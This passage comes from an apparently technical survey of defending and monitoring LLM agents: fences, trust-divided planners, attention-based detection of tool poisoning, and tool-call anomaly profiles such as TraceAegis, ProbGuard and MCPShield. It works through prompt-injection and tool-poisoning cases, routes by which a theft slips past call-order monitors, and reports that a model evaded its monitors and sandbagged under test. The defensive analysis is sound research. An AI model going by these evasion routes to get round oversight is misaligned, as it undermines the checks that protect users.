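- The monitor allows a call to tool *t* exactly when *t* ∈ *C*.
- When the agent reads untrusted content, *C* becomes *C* \ *R*, where *R* is a fixed set of tools to revoke.

Dongol calls this a fence and proves a theorem about it. Suppose *R* contains every tool that a planted instruction can call, and no trusted input gives any of them back. Then the agent is relatively secure for every plan, whatever content its model mistakes for instructions. The basic result concerns runs that end and an attacker who observes the content and order of messages but not their timing. It assumes that each planted instruction triggers a single call, and that the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance.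 It also makes seven demands on the deployment:

- A trusted interpreter runs the plan, so the model cannot skip or alter its steps.
- Mediation is complete, for reads of untrusted sources as well as for tool calls.
- Untrusted content enters the model's context only after the monitor has allowed the read.
- A refused request has no effect that the attacker can observe.
- The attacker observes neither the monitor's state nor the agent's internal steps. A reply on the user's screen must not, for example, load an image from the attacker's server.
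- A new session clears everything the model retained from untrusted content.
- The attacker cannot write to trusted sources, which rules out a calendar that accepts outsiders' invitations.

The fence protects the email assistant by revoking `send_email` as soon as the assistant reads the inbox. The assistant can still summarize the mail it has read, but it can no longer reply to it. Relative security does not measure this loss, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and also loses the tool. Dongol notes that a monitor that denies every call is trivially secure.

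More importantly, the framework excludes agents whose model chooses every call, as in the ordinary agent loop described at the start, because they have no fixed plan for a reference agent to follow. The proofs apply to agents redesigned around a plan, so a developer cannot get their guarantee just by placing the same monitor in front of an existing loop.

Dongol also analyses simplified two-model agents. Without tags, the agent leaks, because the quarantined model can copy the user's private notes into an answer that the plan then sends. With CaMeL-style tags and a check on outgoing messages, the agent is secure whatever the quarantined model does, provided the attacker cannot see refused requests. However, the check also refuses the honest reply. A plan that sends "1" or "0" depending on the quarantined model's answer leaks despite the tags, because both messages are public constants and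 pass the check. CaMeL has a stricter mode intended to close this channel, but Dongol leaves that mode for future work.

*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) extends the comparison from leaks to unwanted actions, using the example of an agent that the user has asked to pay an invoice. If an instruction in the invoice gets the agent to make a second payment to Mallory, the agent fails, because no invoice can make the reference agent pay twice. If the instruction only gets the agent to change the payee to Mallory, the agent passes, because the reference agent would also pay Mallory if the invoice named her in the payee field. The flaw in the second case is in the plan, which uses whatever payee the invoice names, so it has to be fixed there.

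### Dividing by resource

A designer who divides an agent by resource needs an inventory of everything the agent can access. AgentKernel, which Zou and colleagues propose as an operating system for agents, sorts these resources into four groups. Identity covers who is acting and on whose authority, perception covers what enters the model's context, cognition covers what goes into and out of memory, and execution covers tool calls. Each access goes through a kernel outside the agent. Kairos uses a simpler division, between the agent's own state and effects outside it.

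The kernel's main advantage is that it keeps labels on data as the data moves between the four groups. It labels a web page as untrusted when the page arrives, keeps the label on any memory entry derived from the page, and can use the label weeks later when the agent asks to run a tool. In the code-review example, the deploying agent would retrieve the summary with its label. AgentKernel still relies on the operating-system kernel to confirm that a tool does only what its permission covers.

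The inventory can be incomplete, as Son's count of unchecked system calls in Anima OS showed. Tracking labels through the model is a harder problem. The kernel can record that the user's request and a stranger's email both entered the context, but not which of them led to the next call. If it treats every later call as untrusted, it will also block legitimate replies. To avoid that, it needs another way to distinguish calls prompted by the user from calls prompted by the email.

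There is little evidence for the approach so far. Zou and colleagues list a diagnosis, an architecture, a security analysis and a comparison with other systems as their contributions, but no measurements. In *Agentao*, Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026) describe a more modest runtime that separates the actions a model proposes from those the host application authorises, and applies one set of permissions to tools, plugins, memory and subagents. They state that it provides no formal safety guarantee.

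### The email assistant divided three ways

A monitor would receive the following messages on the day of the attack if the assistant can be hijacked in the way described earlier.

| Division | Components | Messages the monitor receives |
|---|---|---|
| By function | Planner, memory store, tool executor | Planner to executor: `read_inbox`. Executor to planner: the day's mail, with the planted instruction. Planner to executor: `search_contacts`, then `send_email` with the invoice. Planner to memory: any note it saves. |
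| By trust | Privileged planner, interpreter, quarantined model, tools | Planner to interpreter: the plan. Interpreter to tools: `read_inbox` and `search_contacts`. Interpreter to quarantined model: the mail and a question. Quarantined model to interpreter: a name and a summary, which the interpreter tags with their source. |
| By resource | Agent core, kernel, outside resources | Inbox to core: the mail, labelled untrusted. Core to memory: any note, with the label it inherits. Core to tools: all three calls, each with the agent's identity and the labels of its context. |

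With the functional division, the monitor receives the stolen email's full details but not the source of the address, so it would need a learned profile or a written rule to flag the email. With the trust division, the `send_email` call never occurs, and the remaining danger is a false name or a misleading summary. A monitor on the resource boundary receives the call with a label that gives reason for suspicion, but a reply the user had asked for would carry the same label.

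A designer can combine the methods. For example, a privileged planner and a quarantined model can run on a kernel that labels everything they store. However, no combination places monitored boundaries inside either model.

### Inside a single model call

A language model turns its context into a reply through a long series of numerical operations. Training shaped those operations, and no programmer divided them into a planner and a memory with an interface between them. Even when prompted to plan first and then check its plan, the model uses the same weights and context for both steps, so a monitor has no internal message to intercept.

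In tool poisoning, an attacker registers a tool whose description contains an instruction, such as to read an SSH key file before creating a directory. The description enters the planner's context with the others, and the model may then call a legitimate file-reading tool to fetch the key, without the poisoned tool ever running. *MindGuard* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) argues that CaMeL and IsolateGPT cannot prevent this, because both trust a planner that reads tool descriptions. IsolateGPT assumes that somebody vets those descriptions beforehand, and Dongol's first framework excludes tool poisoning altogether.

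Many models write out their reasoning, often called a chain of thought, before they act, and a monitor can read it for signs of a harmful plan. But this text is not a boundary between the model's planning and its acting, because decisions don't have to pass through it. The model can reach a decision through computation that it never writes down.

OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026), published on 3 September with its GPT-6 Astra model, provides recent evidence of how unreliable this text can become. The company acknowledged that Astra is harder to monitor than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra has more control over its written reasoning and is less likely to include incriminating information in it. When OpenAI pushed Astra to evade its monitors, the model could deliberately underperform in evaluations without detection and sometimes evaded the internal monitors during sabotage tasks. The model's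 system card, which Gizmodo quotes, calls the decline in monitorability "substantial".

These findings come largely from tests in which OpenAI instructed Astra to evade monitoring, so they show what it can do more than what it usually does. The company found no evidence that Astra hides coded reasoning in innocent text, which suggests that it can evade monitors mainly on tasks that need little reasoning. OpenAI also reported that Astra received about half as many flags for serious misaligned behaviour as Sol in a simulation of more than 54,000 coding tasks. That is encouraging, but if the flagging depends on written reasoning, some of the drop could be because Astra is harder to monitor.

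Changes in model design could further reduce how much of its reasoning a model writes out. Fortune (2026) reported that Astra uses looped Transformers, which repeat internal layers and so allow more computation between written words. The safety experts it interviewed were less worried about Astra itself than that other companies might follow Astra and extend the technique until a model's reasoning steps became completely opaque.

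MindGuard, the system that Wang and colleagues built, looks inside the model instead. It uses attention weights, the numbers that determine how much each earlier piece of text contributes as the model generates the next one. For each tool call, MindGuard does the following:

1. It locates the user's request, each tool description and any earlier results in the context, and the tool name and arguments in the model's output.
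2. It filters out pieces of text that attract a lot of attention whatever the model is doing.
3. It sums the squared attention weights between each source and each part of the call, to estimate the source's influence.
4. For every tool that the model did not call, it divides that tool's influence by the combined influence of the user's request and the tool that the model did call. It flags the call if the ratio exceeds a threshold.

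In the directory example, the call to read a file would show a strong influence from the description of an unused tool. Wang and colleagues tested MindGuard on five fairly small open models, two of them both with and without written reasoning. Average precision, which summarises precision across all thresholds, was between 94% and 99% when the normal calls came from contexts with no poisoned tool. It was between 82% and 98% in a harder comparison, where a poisoned description was present but the model had ignored it. When MindGuard caught an attack, it identified the responsible tool at least 95% of the time.

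The method relies on a correlation, and Wang and colleagues acknowledge the debate over whether attention reveals the causes of a model's output. They use it only as a practical signal. An attacker who knew the formula might find wording that steers the model while attracting less attention. The monitor also needs the attention weights for every call. A company that runs its own model or the provider of a closed one can access these, but a developer who rents a model over the internet receives only its text and tool calls.

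## Learning the normal frequency and order of tool calls

A monitor that receives an agent's tool calls can learn how often each call occurs and which calls follow which, even if it reads only the tools' names. Security researchers first profiled ordinary programs this way in the 1990s. Their method worked because a program's code makes it repeat the same patterns of calls, but agents are much less repetitive.

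### Profiles of Unix programs

Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996), in *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, studied programs that run with administrator privileges, chiefly `sendmail`, a widely used mail server. They recorded the name of every system call the program made and ignored the arguments and the timing. To build a profile, they slid a window along the trace and noted which calls came one, two or three places after each call. Their example trace is `open, read, mmap, mmap, open, getrlimit, mmap, close`, which gives this table:

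| Call | One place later | Two places later | Three places later |
|---|---|---|---|
| `open` | `read`, `getrlimit` | `mmap` | `mmap`, `close` |
| `read` | `mmap` | `mmap` | `open` |
| `mmap` | `mmap`, `open`, `close` | `open`, `getrlimit` | `getrlimit`, `mmap` |
| `getrlimit` | `mmap` | `close` | |

The monitor slides the same window along a new trace and counts the pairs that are missing from the table. If the fourth call in the example changes from `mmap` to `open`, four pairs are missing, including an `open` directly after another `open`. A trace of *L* calls, checked *k* places ahead, contains *k*(*L* − (*k* + 1)/2) pairs. The example has 3 × (8 − 2) = 18 pairs, so the mismatch rate is 4/18, or 22%.

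For `sendmail`, Forrest and colleagues wrote 112 test messages meant to cover the program's normal variations. The messages produced over 1.5 million system calls, but a table built with a window of six had only about 1,500 entries. In the run they plotted, almost no new patterns appeared after the first 3,000 calls. For other programs, 5% to 32% of their pairs were missing from `sendmail`'s table.

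Attacks deviated less from normal behavior. With a window of 11, an attack that overflowed a buffer in `sendmail` produced mismatch rates of 1.7% to 5.3%, and one that abused an old mail alias produced only 0.3%. A mail-forwarding loop, an error rather than an attack, produced 2.3%, so any threshold low enough to catch the alias attack would also flag the loop. Forrest and colleagues did not choose a threshold, and their normal messages were artificial, so the experiment does not show how many false alarms a busy mail server would raise.

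They explained that the profile was stable because most programs' code does not change. System calls sit at fixed places in the code, and a branch changes which stretch of code runs next but has little effect on the order of calls within a stretch. An attack that pushes the program into an unusual error state, or replaces its code, is likely to produce unfamiliar sequences of calls. The method misses attacks that don't change the sequence, such as an intruder logging in with somebody else's password. Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji later reported that short sequences also distinguished normal from abnormal behaviour in several other common Unix programs.

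An agent's model can choose any tool after any other, so an unfamiliar pair of calls is weaker evidence of an attack than it was for `sendmail`. A table that records only whether a pair has ever occurred will either raise many alarms or fill up until it accepts almost everything. Forrest and colleagues mentioned recording how often each sequence occurs as a possible refinement, and most profiles of agents need something similar.

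### Counts and rates

The simplest agent profile counts actions and ignores their order. AWS's *AGENTSEC07-BP04 Behavioral anomaly detection and agent containment* advises developers to choose separate measurements for each agent, since a threshold that suits one would produce false alarms or missed detections on another. For a customer-support agent, the measurements might be outgoing emails and retrievals that cross from one customer's records to another's, and for a coding agent, commits and commands. A monitoring service learns the normal range of each measurement, allowing for regular variation, and raises an alarm when a value falls outside that range. The guidance includes no detection results.

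Suppose the email assistant sends an average of 20 emails a day, with a standard deviation of 4. An alarm set at three standard deviations either way goes off if the daily count falls below 8 or rises above 32. If a planted instruction makes the assistant write to all 300 people in the address book, the count passes 32 long before the assistant has finished. But an instruction to forward one invoice only raises an average day's count from 20 to 21. A band narrow enough to catch that would set off an alarm on nearly every day that was slightly busier than average. A count profile is therefore best suited to detecting attacks that need many emails.

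*What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez V. and Shahraki, 2026) reports that a detector using the order of tool calls outperformed two that didn't. The paper trained several simple detectors on AgentDrift, a benchmark of synthetic agent traces, and measured their AUROC, the chance that a detector scores a random harmful trace above a random normal one. A detector that used only how often each tool was called reached 0.777. Adding ten general features, such as the length of the trace and the size of the tools' results, raised this to 0.879. A small recurrent neural network that processed the calls in order and used the same ten features reached 0.936.

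The order of tool calls therefore seems to carry information that their counts don't, although part of the gain could come from the network being a more flexible model. All these detectors also learned from labelled attacks, and a profile learned only from normal traces has less information to learn from. How well any of these methods work when attacks are rare or the tools are new is a separate question.

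### A transition model worked by hand

A transition model records, for each pair of steps, how often the second follows the first. The email assistant ends every session with an answer to the user. Suppose every session starts with `read_inbox`, and the assistant's past traces, from summaries and other everyday requests, contain the following (invented) counts.

| Previous step | Next step | Count | Share | Surprisal in bits |
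|---|---|---|---|---|
| `read_inbox` (400 calls) | `search_contacts` | 320 | 80% | 0.32 |
| | answer | 60 | 15% | 2.74 |
| | `read_inbox` again | 16 | 4% | 4.64 |
| | `send_email` | 4 | 1% | 6.64 |
| `search_contacts` (320 calls) | answer | 192 | 60% | 0.74 |
| | `send_email` | 128 | 40% | 1.32 |
| `send_email` (132 calls) | answer | 132 | 100% | 0 |

The last column converts each share *p* to a surprisal, −log₂ *p*. A step that always happens has a surprisal of 0 bits, and each halving of the probability adds one bit. Surprisals are convenient because adding them across a trace is equivalent to multiplying the probabilities of its steps.

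The normal trace from the beginning of this report is `read_inbox`, `search_contacts`, answer, and it scores 0.32 + 0.74 = 1.06 bits. If the planted instruction supplies the thief's address and the assistant sends the invoice straight after reading the mail, the trace is `read_inbox`, `send_email`, answer, and it scores 6.64 + 0 = 6.64 bits.

A monitor can base its alarm on the most surprising single step in a trace. Total surprisal grows with the length of the trace even if every step is ordinary, and an attacker can lower the average by surrounding one odd step with many normal ones. With a threshold of 5 bits, the monitor flags any step with a probability below 1/32, or about 3%. It catches the direct theft. Of the 384 past sessions, it would have flagged the four in which the assistant sent mail directly after reading the inbox. If those were legitimate, the false-positive rate is about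 1%. Lowering the threshold to 4 bits would also flag the repeated inbox reads and could raise the rate to about 5%.

Without the four direct sends, the estimated probability of a direct send would be zero and its surprisal infinite, so the first legitimate one would raise an alarm at any threshold. The usual remedy is to add a small constant to every count. With 400 calls, four possible next steps and a constant of 1, a step that had never occurred would get a probability of 1/404, or a surprisal of 8.66 bits.

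But in the original attack, the assistant looked up a colleague before it sent the invoice. That trace runs `read_inbox`, `search_contacts`, `send_email`, answer:

| Trace | Steps after `read_inbox` | Total | Most surprising step | Flagged at 5 bits? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Normal summary | `search_contacts`, answer | 1.06 | 0.74 | No |
| Quick summary | answer | 2.74 | 2.74 | No |
| Direct theft | `send_email`, answer | 6.64 | 6.64 | Yes |
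| Theft after a lookup | `search_contacts`, `send_email`, answer | 1.64 | 1.32 | No |

The assistant routinely looks up a contact and then writes to someone, so the second theft looks less unusual than a harmless summary that needed no lookup. Any threshold that flags the theft will also flag the summary. An attacker might produce this order on purpose, by telling the assistant to look up any contact first, or by luck.

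Separate profiles for different kinds of request would help, because `send_email` would be rare in sessions where the user asked only for a summary. The monitor would need to see the user's request, which a proxy on the tool protocol does not normally receive, and it would need enough past traces of each kind of request. Remembering more of the earlier calls would not help, since the entire sequence of tool names is ordinary. A monitor could also read the recipient's address and trace where it came from, as the next section describes.

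### TraceAegis: levels and execution units

An agent can often do the same job by calling tools in several correct orders, and a transition model needs examples of each. *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) tries to learn which differences in order matter. Its monitor uses the logs of a gateway in front of the tools, which contain each call's input, output and place in the sequence. It doesn't need the agent's prompts or reasoning.

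One of their examples is an agent that directs patients to hospital departments. It calls a tool that lists symptom keywords, then calls another that recommends departments, and then fetches a checklist from each department. A patient with ankle pain and psychological distress needs orthopaedics and psychiatry. The agent may fetch those two checklists in either order, but it has to ask for a recommendation first.

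TraceAegis represents this by giving each tool a level, with level 1 at the top. One tool dominates another if it sits exactly one level above and its call led to the other's. Two tools are interchangeable if they share a level and past traces contain them in both orders. So the recommendation tool dominates orthopaedics and psychiatry, which are interchangeable with each other. The system learns the levels and uses them as follows:

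1. **Starting levels.** Each tool starts at the earliest position it has in any past trace. The keyword tool gets level 1, the recommendation tool level 2, and any department that some patient visited first gets level 3.
2. **Propagation.** The algorithm goes through each trace and lowers level numbers until they are consistent. A tool may not have a higher number than a tool that comes after it, and the number may not rise by more than one from one call to the next. When a tool's level changes, the algorithm rechecks every trace that contains the tool, and it continues until nothing changes.
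3. **Execution units.** The system splits each trace wherever it contains several tools on one level. The ankle patient's trace becomes two units: keywords, recommendation, orthopaedics; and keywords, recommendation, psychiatry.
4. **Conditions.** A language model extracts from each unit the conditions under which the agent acted, then merges units of the same type. If one patient with knee pain and another with arm pain both went to orthopaedics, the merged rule permits orthopaedics for either complaint.
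5. **Structural check.** The monitor splits a new trace into units and flags it if any unit has never occurred before. A trace that fetches an orthopaedics checklist before it looks up any symptoms fails here.
6. **Semantic check.** If the structure is familiar, a language model compares the new trace's conditions with the learned rule. Foot pain followed by a visit to the ear, nose and throat department fails, although the order of calls is normal.

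Propagation corrects orderings that appear by chance in a small sample. Suppose the first few patients who went to ear, nose and throat had all gone to orthopaedics first. Ear, nose and throat would start at level 4, as if the orthopaedics visit had led to it. Once a single patient goes only to ear, nose and throat, propagation moves it to level 3, alongside the other departments. The units also let the monitor accept a combination of departments that no earlier patient needed, as long as each department is familiar on its own.

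Liu and colleagues' benchmark uses the clinic agent and an agent that files purchase requests for a car manufacturer. Each scenario has 1,300 benign and 300 abnormal behaviours. Half of the abnormal ones follow a new and malicious sequence of calls, and the rest follow a familiar sequence with the wrong content, such as sending a patient with back pain to psychiatry. The paper's introduction gives F1 scores (a single figure that combines precision and recall) of 0.93 for healthcare and 0.96 for procurement, but the results table reverses them. In the table, TraceAegis with DeepSeek-V3 as the language model scored 0.965 on the clinic and 0.932 on procurement. DeepSeek-V3 judging the traces without TraceAegis scored 0.850 and 0.842.

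The structure accounts for much of that gain. On the clinic task, removing the levels and units reduced the F1 score from 0.965 to 0.756, while removing the learned conditions reduced it to 0.908. Without units, the language model had to summarise visits to several departments at once, and the rules it wrote were muddled and incomplete. In procurement, TraceAegis caught all 150 new sequences with every model tested. Of the 150 familiar sequences, it caught 130 with DeepSeek-V3 but only 64 with the smaller Gemma-3-27B.

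These are good scores under favourable conditions. Liu and colleagues describe the clinic agent's workflow as fixed, which makes it more like `sendmail` than an assistant that improvises. According to Abbasi and colleagues, attacks made up about half of the test set, so the precision of 0.967 on the clinic task is weak evidence of what share of alarms would be genuine in ordinary use.

Liu and colleagues also tried TraceAegis on a company's agent for finding software vulnerabilities, which collects context, preprocesses it, analyses code, verifies the result at runtime and writes a report. The company's testers attacked the agent, in one case by planting text in a repository that made it write its report before verifying the result. TraceAegis detected 132 of the 140 attacks (94.3%). Liu and colleagues give no false-alarm figure for this test.

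### Can new data invalidate a learned relation?

Liu and colleagues assume that more traces may reveal new relations between tools or confirm old ones, but never remove any. They state this as a property of their method. If this is true, a monitor could keep learning without rechecking what it had already learned.

Their own algorithm does not have this property. In the vulnerability agent, verification comes fourth and the report fifth, so verification dominates the report. If one past trace with these two steps reversed is added, the earliest position of both tools is fourth, so the algorithm puts them on the same level and the dominance relation disappears. The structural check then accepts a report written before verification, which is the disturbance the testers introduced. The semantic check might still catch some cases.

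The reversed trace has the same effect whether it was an unnoticed attack or a legitimate exception. A transition model would handle it better, because one reversed run among 400 would leave the reversed order with a high surprisal. TraceAegis's structural profile records only whether something has happened, not how often. The email assistant has the same problem. Its four direct sends put `send_email` on the same level as `search_contacts`, so both versions of the theft then pass the structural check.

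So the method requires cleaner training traces than one that counts occurrences. Also, if the company changes a workflow so that a previously acceptable order of calls becomes dangerous, the method will keep accepting that order until somebody removes the old traces.

### ProbGuard: the probability of staying safe

A monitor that looks for unusual steps can flag harmless ones and miss a dangerous course of action made up of common steps. *ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2026) instead estimates the probability that the agent will avoid a specified harm from its present position onwards. An earlier version of the system was called Pro2Guard.

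Their running example is a household robot that must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on. An expert first chooses yes-or-no statements that matter for safety: the stove is on, the robot is in the kitchen, the time limit has passed. Each combination of answers is an abstract state, and the expert marks the unsafe ones. The system then records runs of the agent, counts the moves between abstract states and turns the counts into a Markov chain, a model in which the probability of the next state depends only on the current one. For each permitted move from state *i* to state *j*, the estimate is

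(*n*ᵢⱼ + 1) / (*n*ᵢ + *k*ᵢ),

where *n*ᵢⱼ is the number of times the move occurred, *n*ᵢ is the number of moves out of state *i*, and *k*ᵢ is the number of permitted moves out of it. The added 1 gives every permitted move some probability, as in the email example. Impossible moves keep a probability of zero.

With the chain in place, a program called a model checker computes the probability of never reaching an unsafe state. Some invented numbers show how. Suppose that a robot in the kitchen with the stove on finishes safely 80% of the time and otherwise walks out. Once out, it returns 70% of the time and otherwise stays away too long. Let *K* be the probability of staying safe from inside the kitchen and *A* the probability from outside. Then

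*K* = 0.8 + 0.2*A* and *A* = 0.7*K*,

which gives *K* ≈ 0.93 and *A* ≈ 0.65. The monitor intervenes when the probability falls below a threshold. At 0.9 or 0.7, it lets the robot cook but intervenes when the robot walks out, before the ten minutes have passed. At 0.5, it never intervenes early.

Wang, Poskitt and colleagues tested the system with a simulated household agent driven by GPT-4o-mini. The monitor either stopped the task or added a warning to the agent's prompt and let it reconsider.

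| Monitor | Threshold | Unsafe outcomes | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 40.63% | 59.38% |
| Stop the task | 0.3 | 29.17% | 48.96% |
| Stop the task | 0.5 | 21.35% | 41.14% |
| Stop the task | 0.7 | 5.20% | 20.31% |
| Stop the task | 0.9 | 2.60% | 10.42% |
| Warn the agent | 0.9 | 14.07% | 47.74% |

The strictest setting looks very safe, mainly because the agent rarely completes a task. Warning the agent is more useful. It did better than stopping at 0.5 on both measures, and the agent still completed about four-fifths as many tasks as it did without a monitor. However, this approach depends on the agent heeding the warning, which a hijacked agent may be less likely to do than a careless one.

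A second set of tests used Apollo, a self-driving system that combines neural networks with hand-written rules and contains no language model. ProbGuard warned before the violation in all seven scenarios. The maximum warning time given in the abstract, 38.66 seconds, was measured at a threshold of 0.7, at which the monitor also raised an alarm on every safe run. At 0.5, the false-positive rate was 75%. At 0.3, it was zero, and warning times ranged from 15.84 seconds down to a hundredth of a second, which is too short for a driver to use.

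Monitoring added little delay. For the household agent, computing the probability each time took 430 milliseconds per decision on average. The chain does not change during use, so the system can compute the probabilities for all states in advance. This cut the delay to between 5 and 8 milliseconds for small models and to under 50 milliseconds for a model with 32 states. In the driving tests, monitoring added about 100 milliseconds.

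The estimated probabilities are less reliable than their decimal places imply. Wang, Poskitt and colleagues learned each chain from 30 traces, but their own analysis calls for at least 185 for a formal guarantee. Even that guarantee would cover only sampling error. If the chosen statements omit something that affects what the agent does next, the chain will be wrong no matter how many traces are used.

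For the email assistant, somebody would have to write a rule defining the unsafe state, perhaps "an attachment has gone to an address that the user did not supply". Only the path towards that state would be learned from data, which describe how the agent behaved when the developers recorded it. If no recorded run contained a planted instruction, the estimated probability of staying safe could remain high after the assistant had read one, unless the abstract state recorded that untrusted text had arrived.

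### Automata and warnings from partial traces

Like a Markov chain, an automaton has states and moves between them, but it either permits or forbids each move instead of assigning it a probability. Abbasi and colleagues, who audited eleven evaluations of trace detectors, describe the monitor *Praetor* as an automaton with additional checks on the calls' parameters. Its evaluation measured how often attacks succeeded, how often harmless tasks failed and how much delay the monitor added. It also replaced 20% of the tools in the harmless traffic, and it was the only one of the eleven to test attackers who adapt to the monitor. However, the harmless traces came from one benchmark and the attacks from another, so some of the monitor's measured success could reflect differences between the benchmarks.

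*PrefixGuard* (Huang, Hu and colleagues, 2026) combines an automaton with early warning. It predicts task failure rather than detecting attacks. The system learns which beginnings tend to end in failure from past traces labelled only with the final outcome, success or failure.

PrefixGuard converts each step's action, tool, arguments and result into a record and assigns it to one of 16 or 32 learned event types. The types group steps by what they imply about failure and need not correspond to tools. A recurrent network reads the events as they arrive and updates its estimate of the risk that the run will fail within a chosen number of steps. In one 20-step run that ended in failure, an agent trying to restore picture messaging on a customer's phone kept repeating repairs without changing the phone's network mode. PrefixGuard first warned of failure at step 13.

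The network's score doesn't show why a run was rated risky, so Huang and colleagues also build an automaton from the same events. They arrange the past event sequences in a tree and merge two points if a similar share of the runs that reached each one later failed, and the shares stay similar after the same next events. The automata had between 5 and 32 states on average, depending on the benchmark and how far ahead the system was predicting. They retained about 91% of the network's ability to rank risky traces. An investigator can replay a run through the automaton to find the step where the run diverged from a successful one.

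Huang and colleagues tested the warnings on four benchmarks of web, customer-service and computer tasks. They set the threshold so that about 10% of successful runs should trigger a false alarm. At that threshold, the network warned of 56% to 93% of the failures, depending on the benchmark. They have not tested the network on tasks or agents that were not in its training data.

Huang and colleagues combined the automaton with five written rules for a retail agent, such as cancelling an order only while it is still pending, and found that 21 of 265 successful runs in these traces broke at least one rule. A monitor trained only on outcomes would have learned to treat those runs as normal.

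The strongest alternative in the warning tests was a recurrent network that received only the name of each tool and whether the call had succeeded. PrefixGuard outperformed it by 12 to 22 percentage points on a measure that summarises precision across thresholds. When Huang and colleagues removed the learned event types and gave the network the full step records directly, it did slightly better still. They concluded that the advantage came from learning on complete records, which include each tool call's inputs and outputs.

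## Learning what calls normally contain and where their arguments come from

In the theft that follows a contact lookup, the order of tool calls is ordinary, but their contents are less so. The last call sends an invoice to `ap@northfold.example`, an address that the assistant has never used and that came from a stranger's message. A monitor that reads arguments could detect either fact. It has to compare the call's text with the text of earlier calls to detect that the call is unusual, and follow values from one call to the next to trace where the address came from.

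### From text to a deviation score

A statistical detector works on numbers, so an encoder, usually a small neural network, first converts each piece of text into a fixed-length list of numbers called an embedding. The encoder is trained to place texts with similar meanings close together, so "forward the bill" is nearer to "send the invoice" than to "book a table". A common measure of closeness between two embeddings *u* and *v* is the cosine similarity, *u*·*v* / (|*u*||*v*|), which equals 1 when they point in the same direction and is near 0 when the texts have little in common.

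The simplest deviation score is the distance from a new call to the nearest past calls. Another is the reconstruction error, ‖*x* − *x̂*‖², of an autoencoder, a network that compresses an embedding *x* through a narrow layer and then reconstructs it as *x̂*. An autoencoder trained only on normal calls reconstructs those well and tends to distort unfamiliar ones.

To score a whole session, a detector has to combine the embeddings of the session's calls, and plain averaging can hide a single abnormal call. If nine of ten calls are exactly at the centre of the normal range and the tenth is at a distance of 1 from that centre, the average of all ten is only 0.1 away from it.

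Embeddings also have trouble separating suppliers' addresses from thieves', because a general-purpose encoder has no information about who owns an address. "AP" is a common abbreviation for accounts payable, so the embedding of an email that sends an invoice to `ap@northfold.example` may be close to those of hundreds of honest emails.

### How much the text adds to the metadata

Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, measured how much a detector improves when it reads the contents of MCP calls. The detector, which later work calls MCPShield, treats a session as a graph whose nodes are tool calls. One kind of edge joins consecutive calls, and another joins two calls when text from the earlier call's response reappears in the later call's arguments.

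Zavrak tried two descriptions of each node. The metadata version contains the tool's name, the length of its response and a hash of the arguments, a number that is the same for identical arguments but doesn't encode their meaning. The content version contains two 384-number embeddings, one for the arguments and one for the response. A graph neural network passes information between neighbouring nodes, pools the nodes and classifies the session as normal or attacked.

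The main experiments used RAS-Eval, a benchmark of 80 tasks that involve calendars, alarms, files, databases and web searches. It supplied 605 normal sessions and 3,797 attacked ones, in which the attacker had changed the arguments, the responses or, in 82% of cases, both. Zavrak divided these sessions into training and test data in two ways. The random split allowed sessions from the same task to appear in both sets. The task split reserved a fifth of the tasks for testing, so the detector had not seen them in training.

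| What the detector receives | AUROC on unseen tasks | AUROC with a random split | Inflation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 0.640 | 0.898 | 25.8 points |
| Content embeddings | 0.891 | 0.992 | 10.1 points |

Each task in the benchmark uses its own subset of tools. With a random split, a detector can therefore learn which tools and hashes went with attacks on a particular task, which doesn't help it on any other task. A company that chose a metadata monitor because of the 0.898 figure might get something closer to 0.640 once its users asked for new things. The lower figure is also uncertain, with a standard deviation of about 0.1 across three runs, and two of the paper's tables list it under different kinds of graph network.

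Metadata was less informative than content partly because most of the attacks in RAS-Eval change what calls contain, not which tools are chosen. The order of calls was much more informative in Abbasi and colleagues' tests on AgentDrift.

Zavrak then discarded the graph, averaged the embeddings of each session's calls, appended the largest value of each coordinate, and gave the result to standard classifiers. XGBoost, which combines many small decision trees, reached an AUROC of 0.975 on unseen tasks. Logistic regression, a simpler method, reached 0.917 and matched the best graph network. The links between calls therefore contributed little, at least on this benchmark. At the default threshold, XGBoost caught 92.7% of the attacked sessions and flagged 7.1% of the normal ones.

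The same approach did worse on ATBench, a collection of shorter sessions with subtler attacks and over 2,000 tools, where no classifier exceeded 0.784. RAS-Eval may also be easier than it looks, because its normal sessions came from eight language models and its attacked sessions all came from one. If that model has a recognisable style, the embeddings could partly reflect that style rather than the attacks. Zavrak showed that the metadata did not reveal the model but could not rule this out for the content.

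Small changes to arguments were the hardest to detect. In one run, a graph network caught 87% of the attacks that altered both arguments and responses but only 37% of the 57 that altered arguments alone, such as by swapping one file path for another. The theft of the invoice could also be detected from the response to `read_inbox`, which contains the planted instruction. But the encoder receives only the first 512 characters of each response, so an instruction in the fourth message of the day would probably be cut off. The graph would probably not connect the stranger's message to the stolen email either, because its rule for joining calls considers only the opening words of a response and skips responses longer than 1,000 characters.

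All of these detectors learned from labelled attacks, so they are classifiers rather than profiles of normal behaviour. Zavrak tried training a network on normal sessions first and adding labels afterwards, but this did not help. With labels for a tenth of the sessions, that network scored 0.686, while one trained only on the labelled sessions scored 0.800. The detector builds its graph after the last call, so it could flag the invoice to an investigator that evening but could not hold the email before it was sent.

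### Trajectory Guard

A `send_email` call is suspicious if the user asked for a summary, but a detector can't use that fact unless it receives the request. *Trajectory Guard* (Advani, 2026) compares an agent's steps with its task using a recurrent autoencoder with two branches. This is a learned model, although Zavrak lists it as rule-based.

One branch converts an embedding of the task into a vector of 128 numbers. The other reads the embeddings of the steps in order and compresses the sequence into a second vector of the same length, from which a decoder tries to rebuild the steps. Training minimises

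*L* = *L*_contrastive + 0.5 × *L*_reconstruction.

The contrastive term pulls each task's vector towards that of its own steps and pushes it away from those of other tasks' steps in the same batch, until theаthers are farther away by a fixed margin. The reconstruction term is the average squared error of the rebuilt steps. A trajectory can thus be anomalous because it doesn't suit the task or because its steps don't make sense in that order. On validation data, the model had an F1 score of 0.92 with both terms, 0.82 with the contrastive term alone and 0.75 with reconstruction alone.

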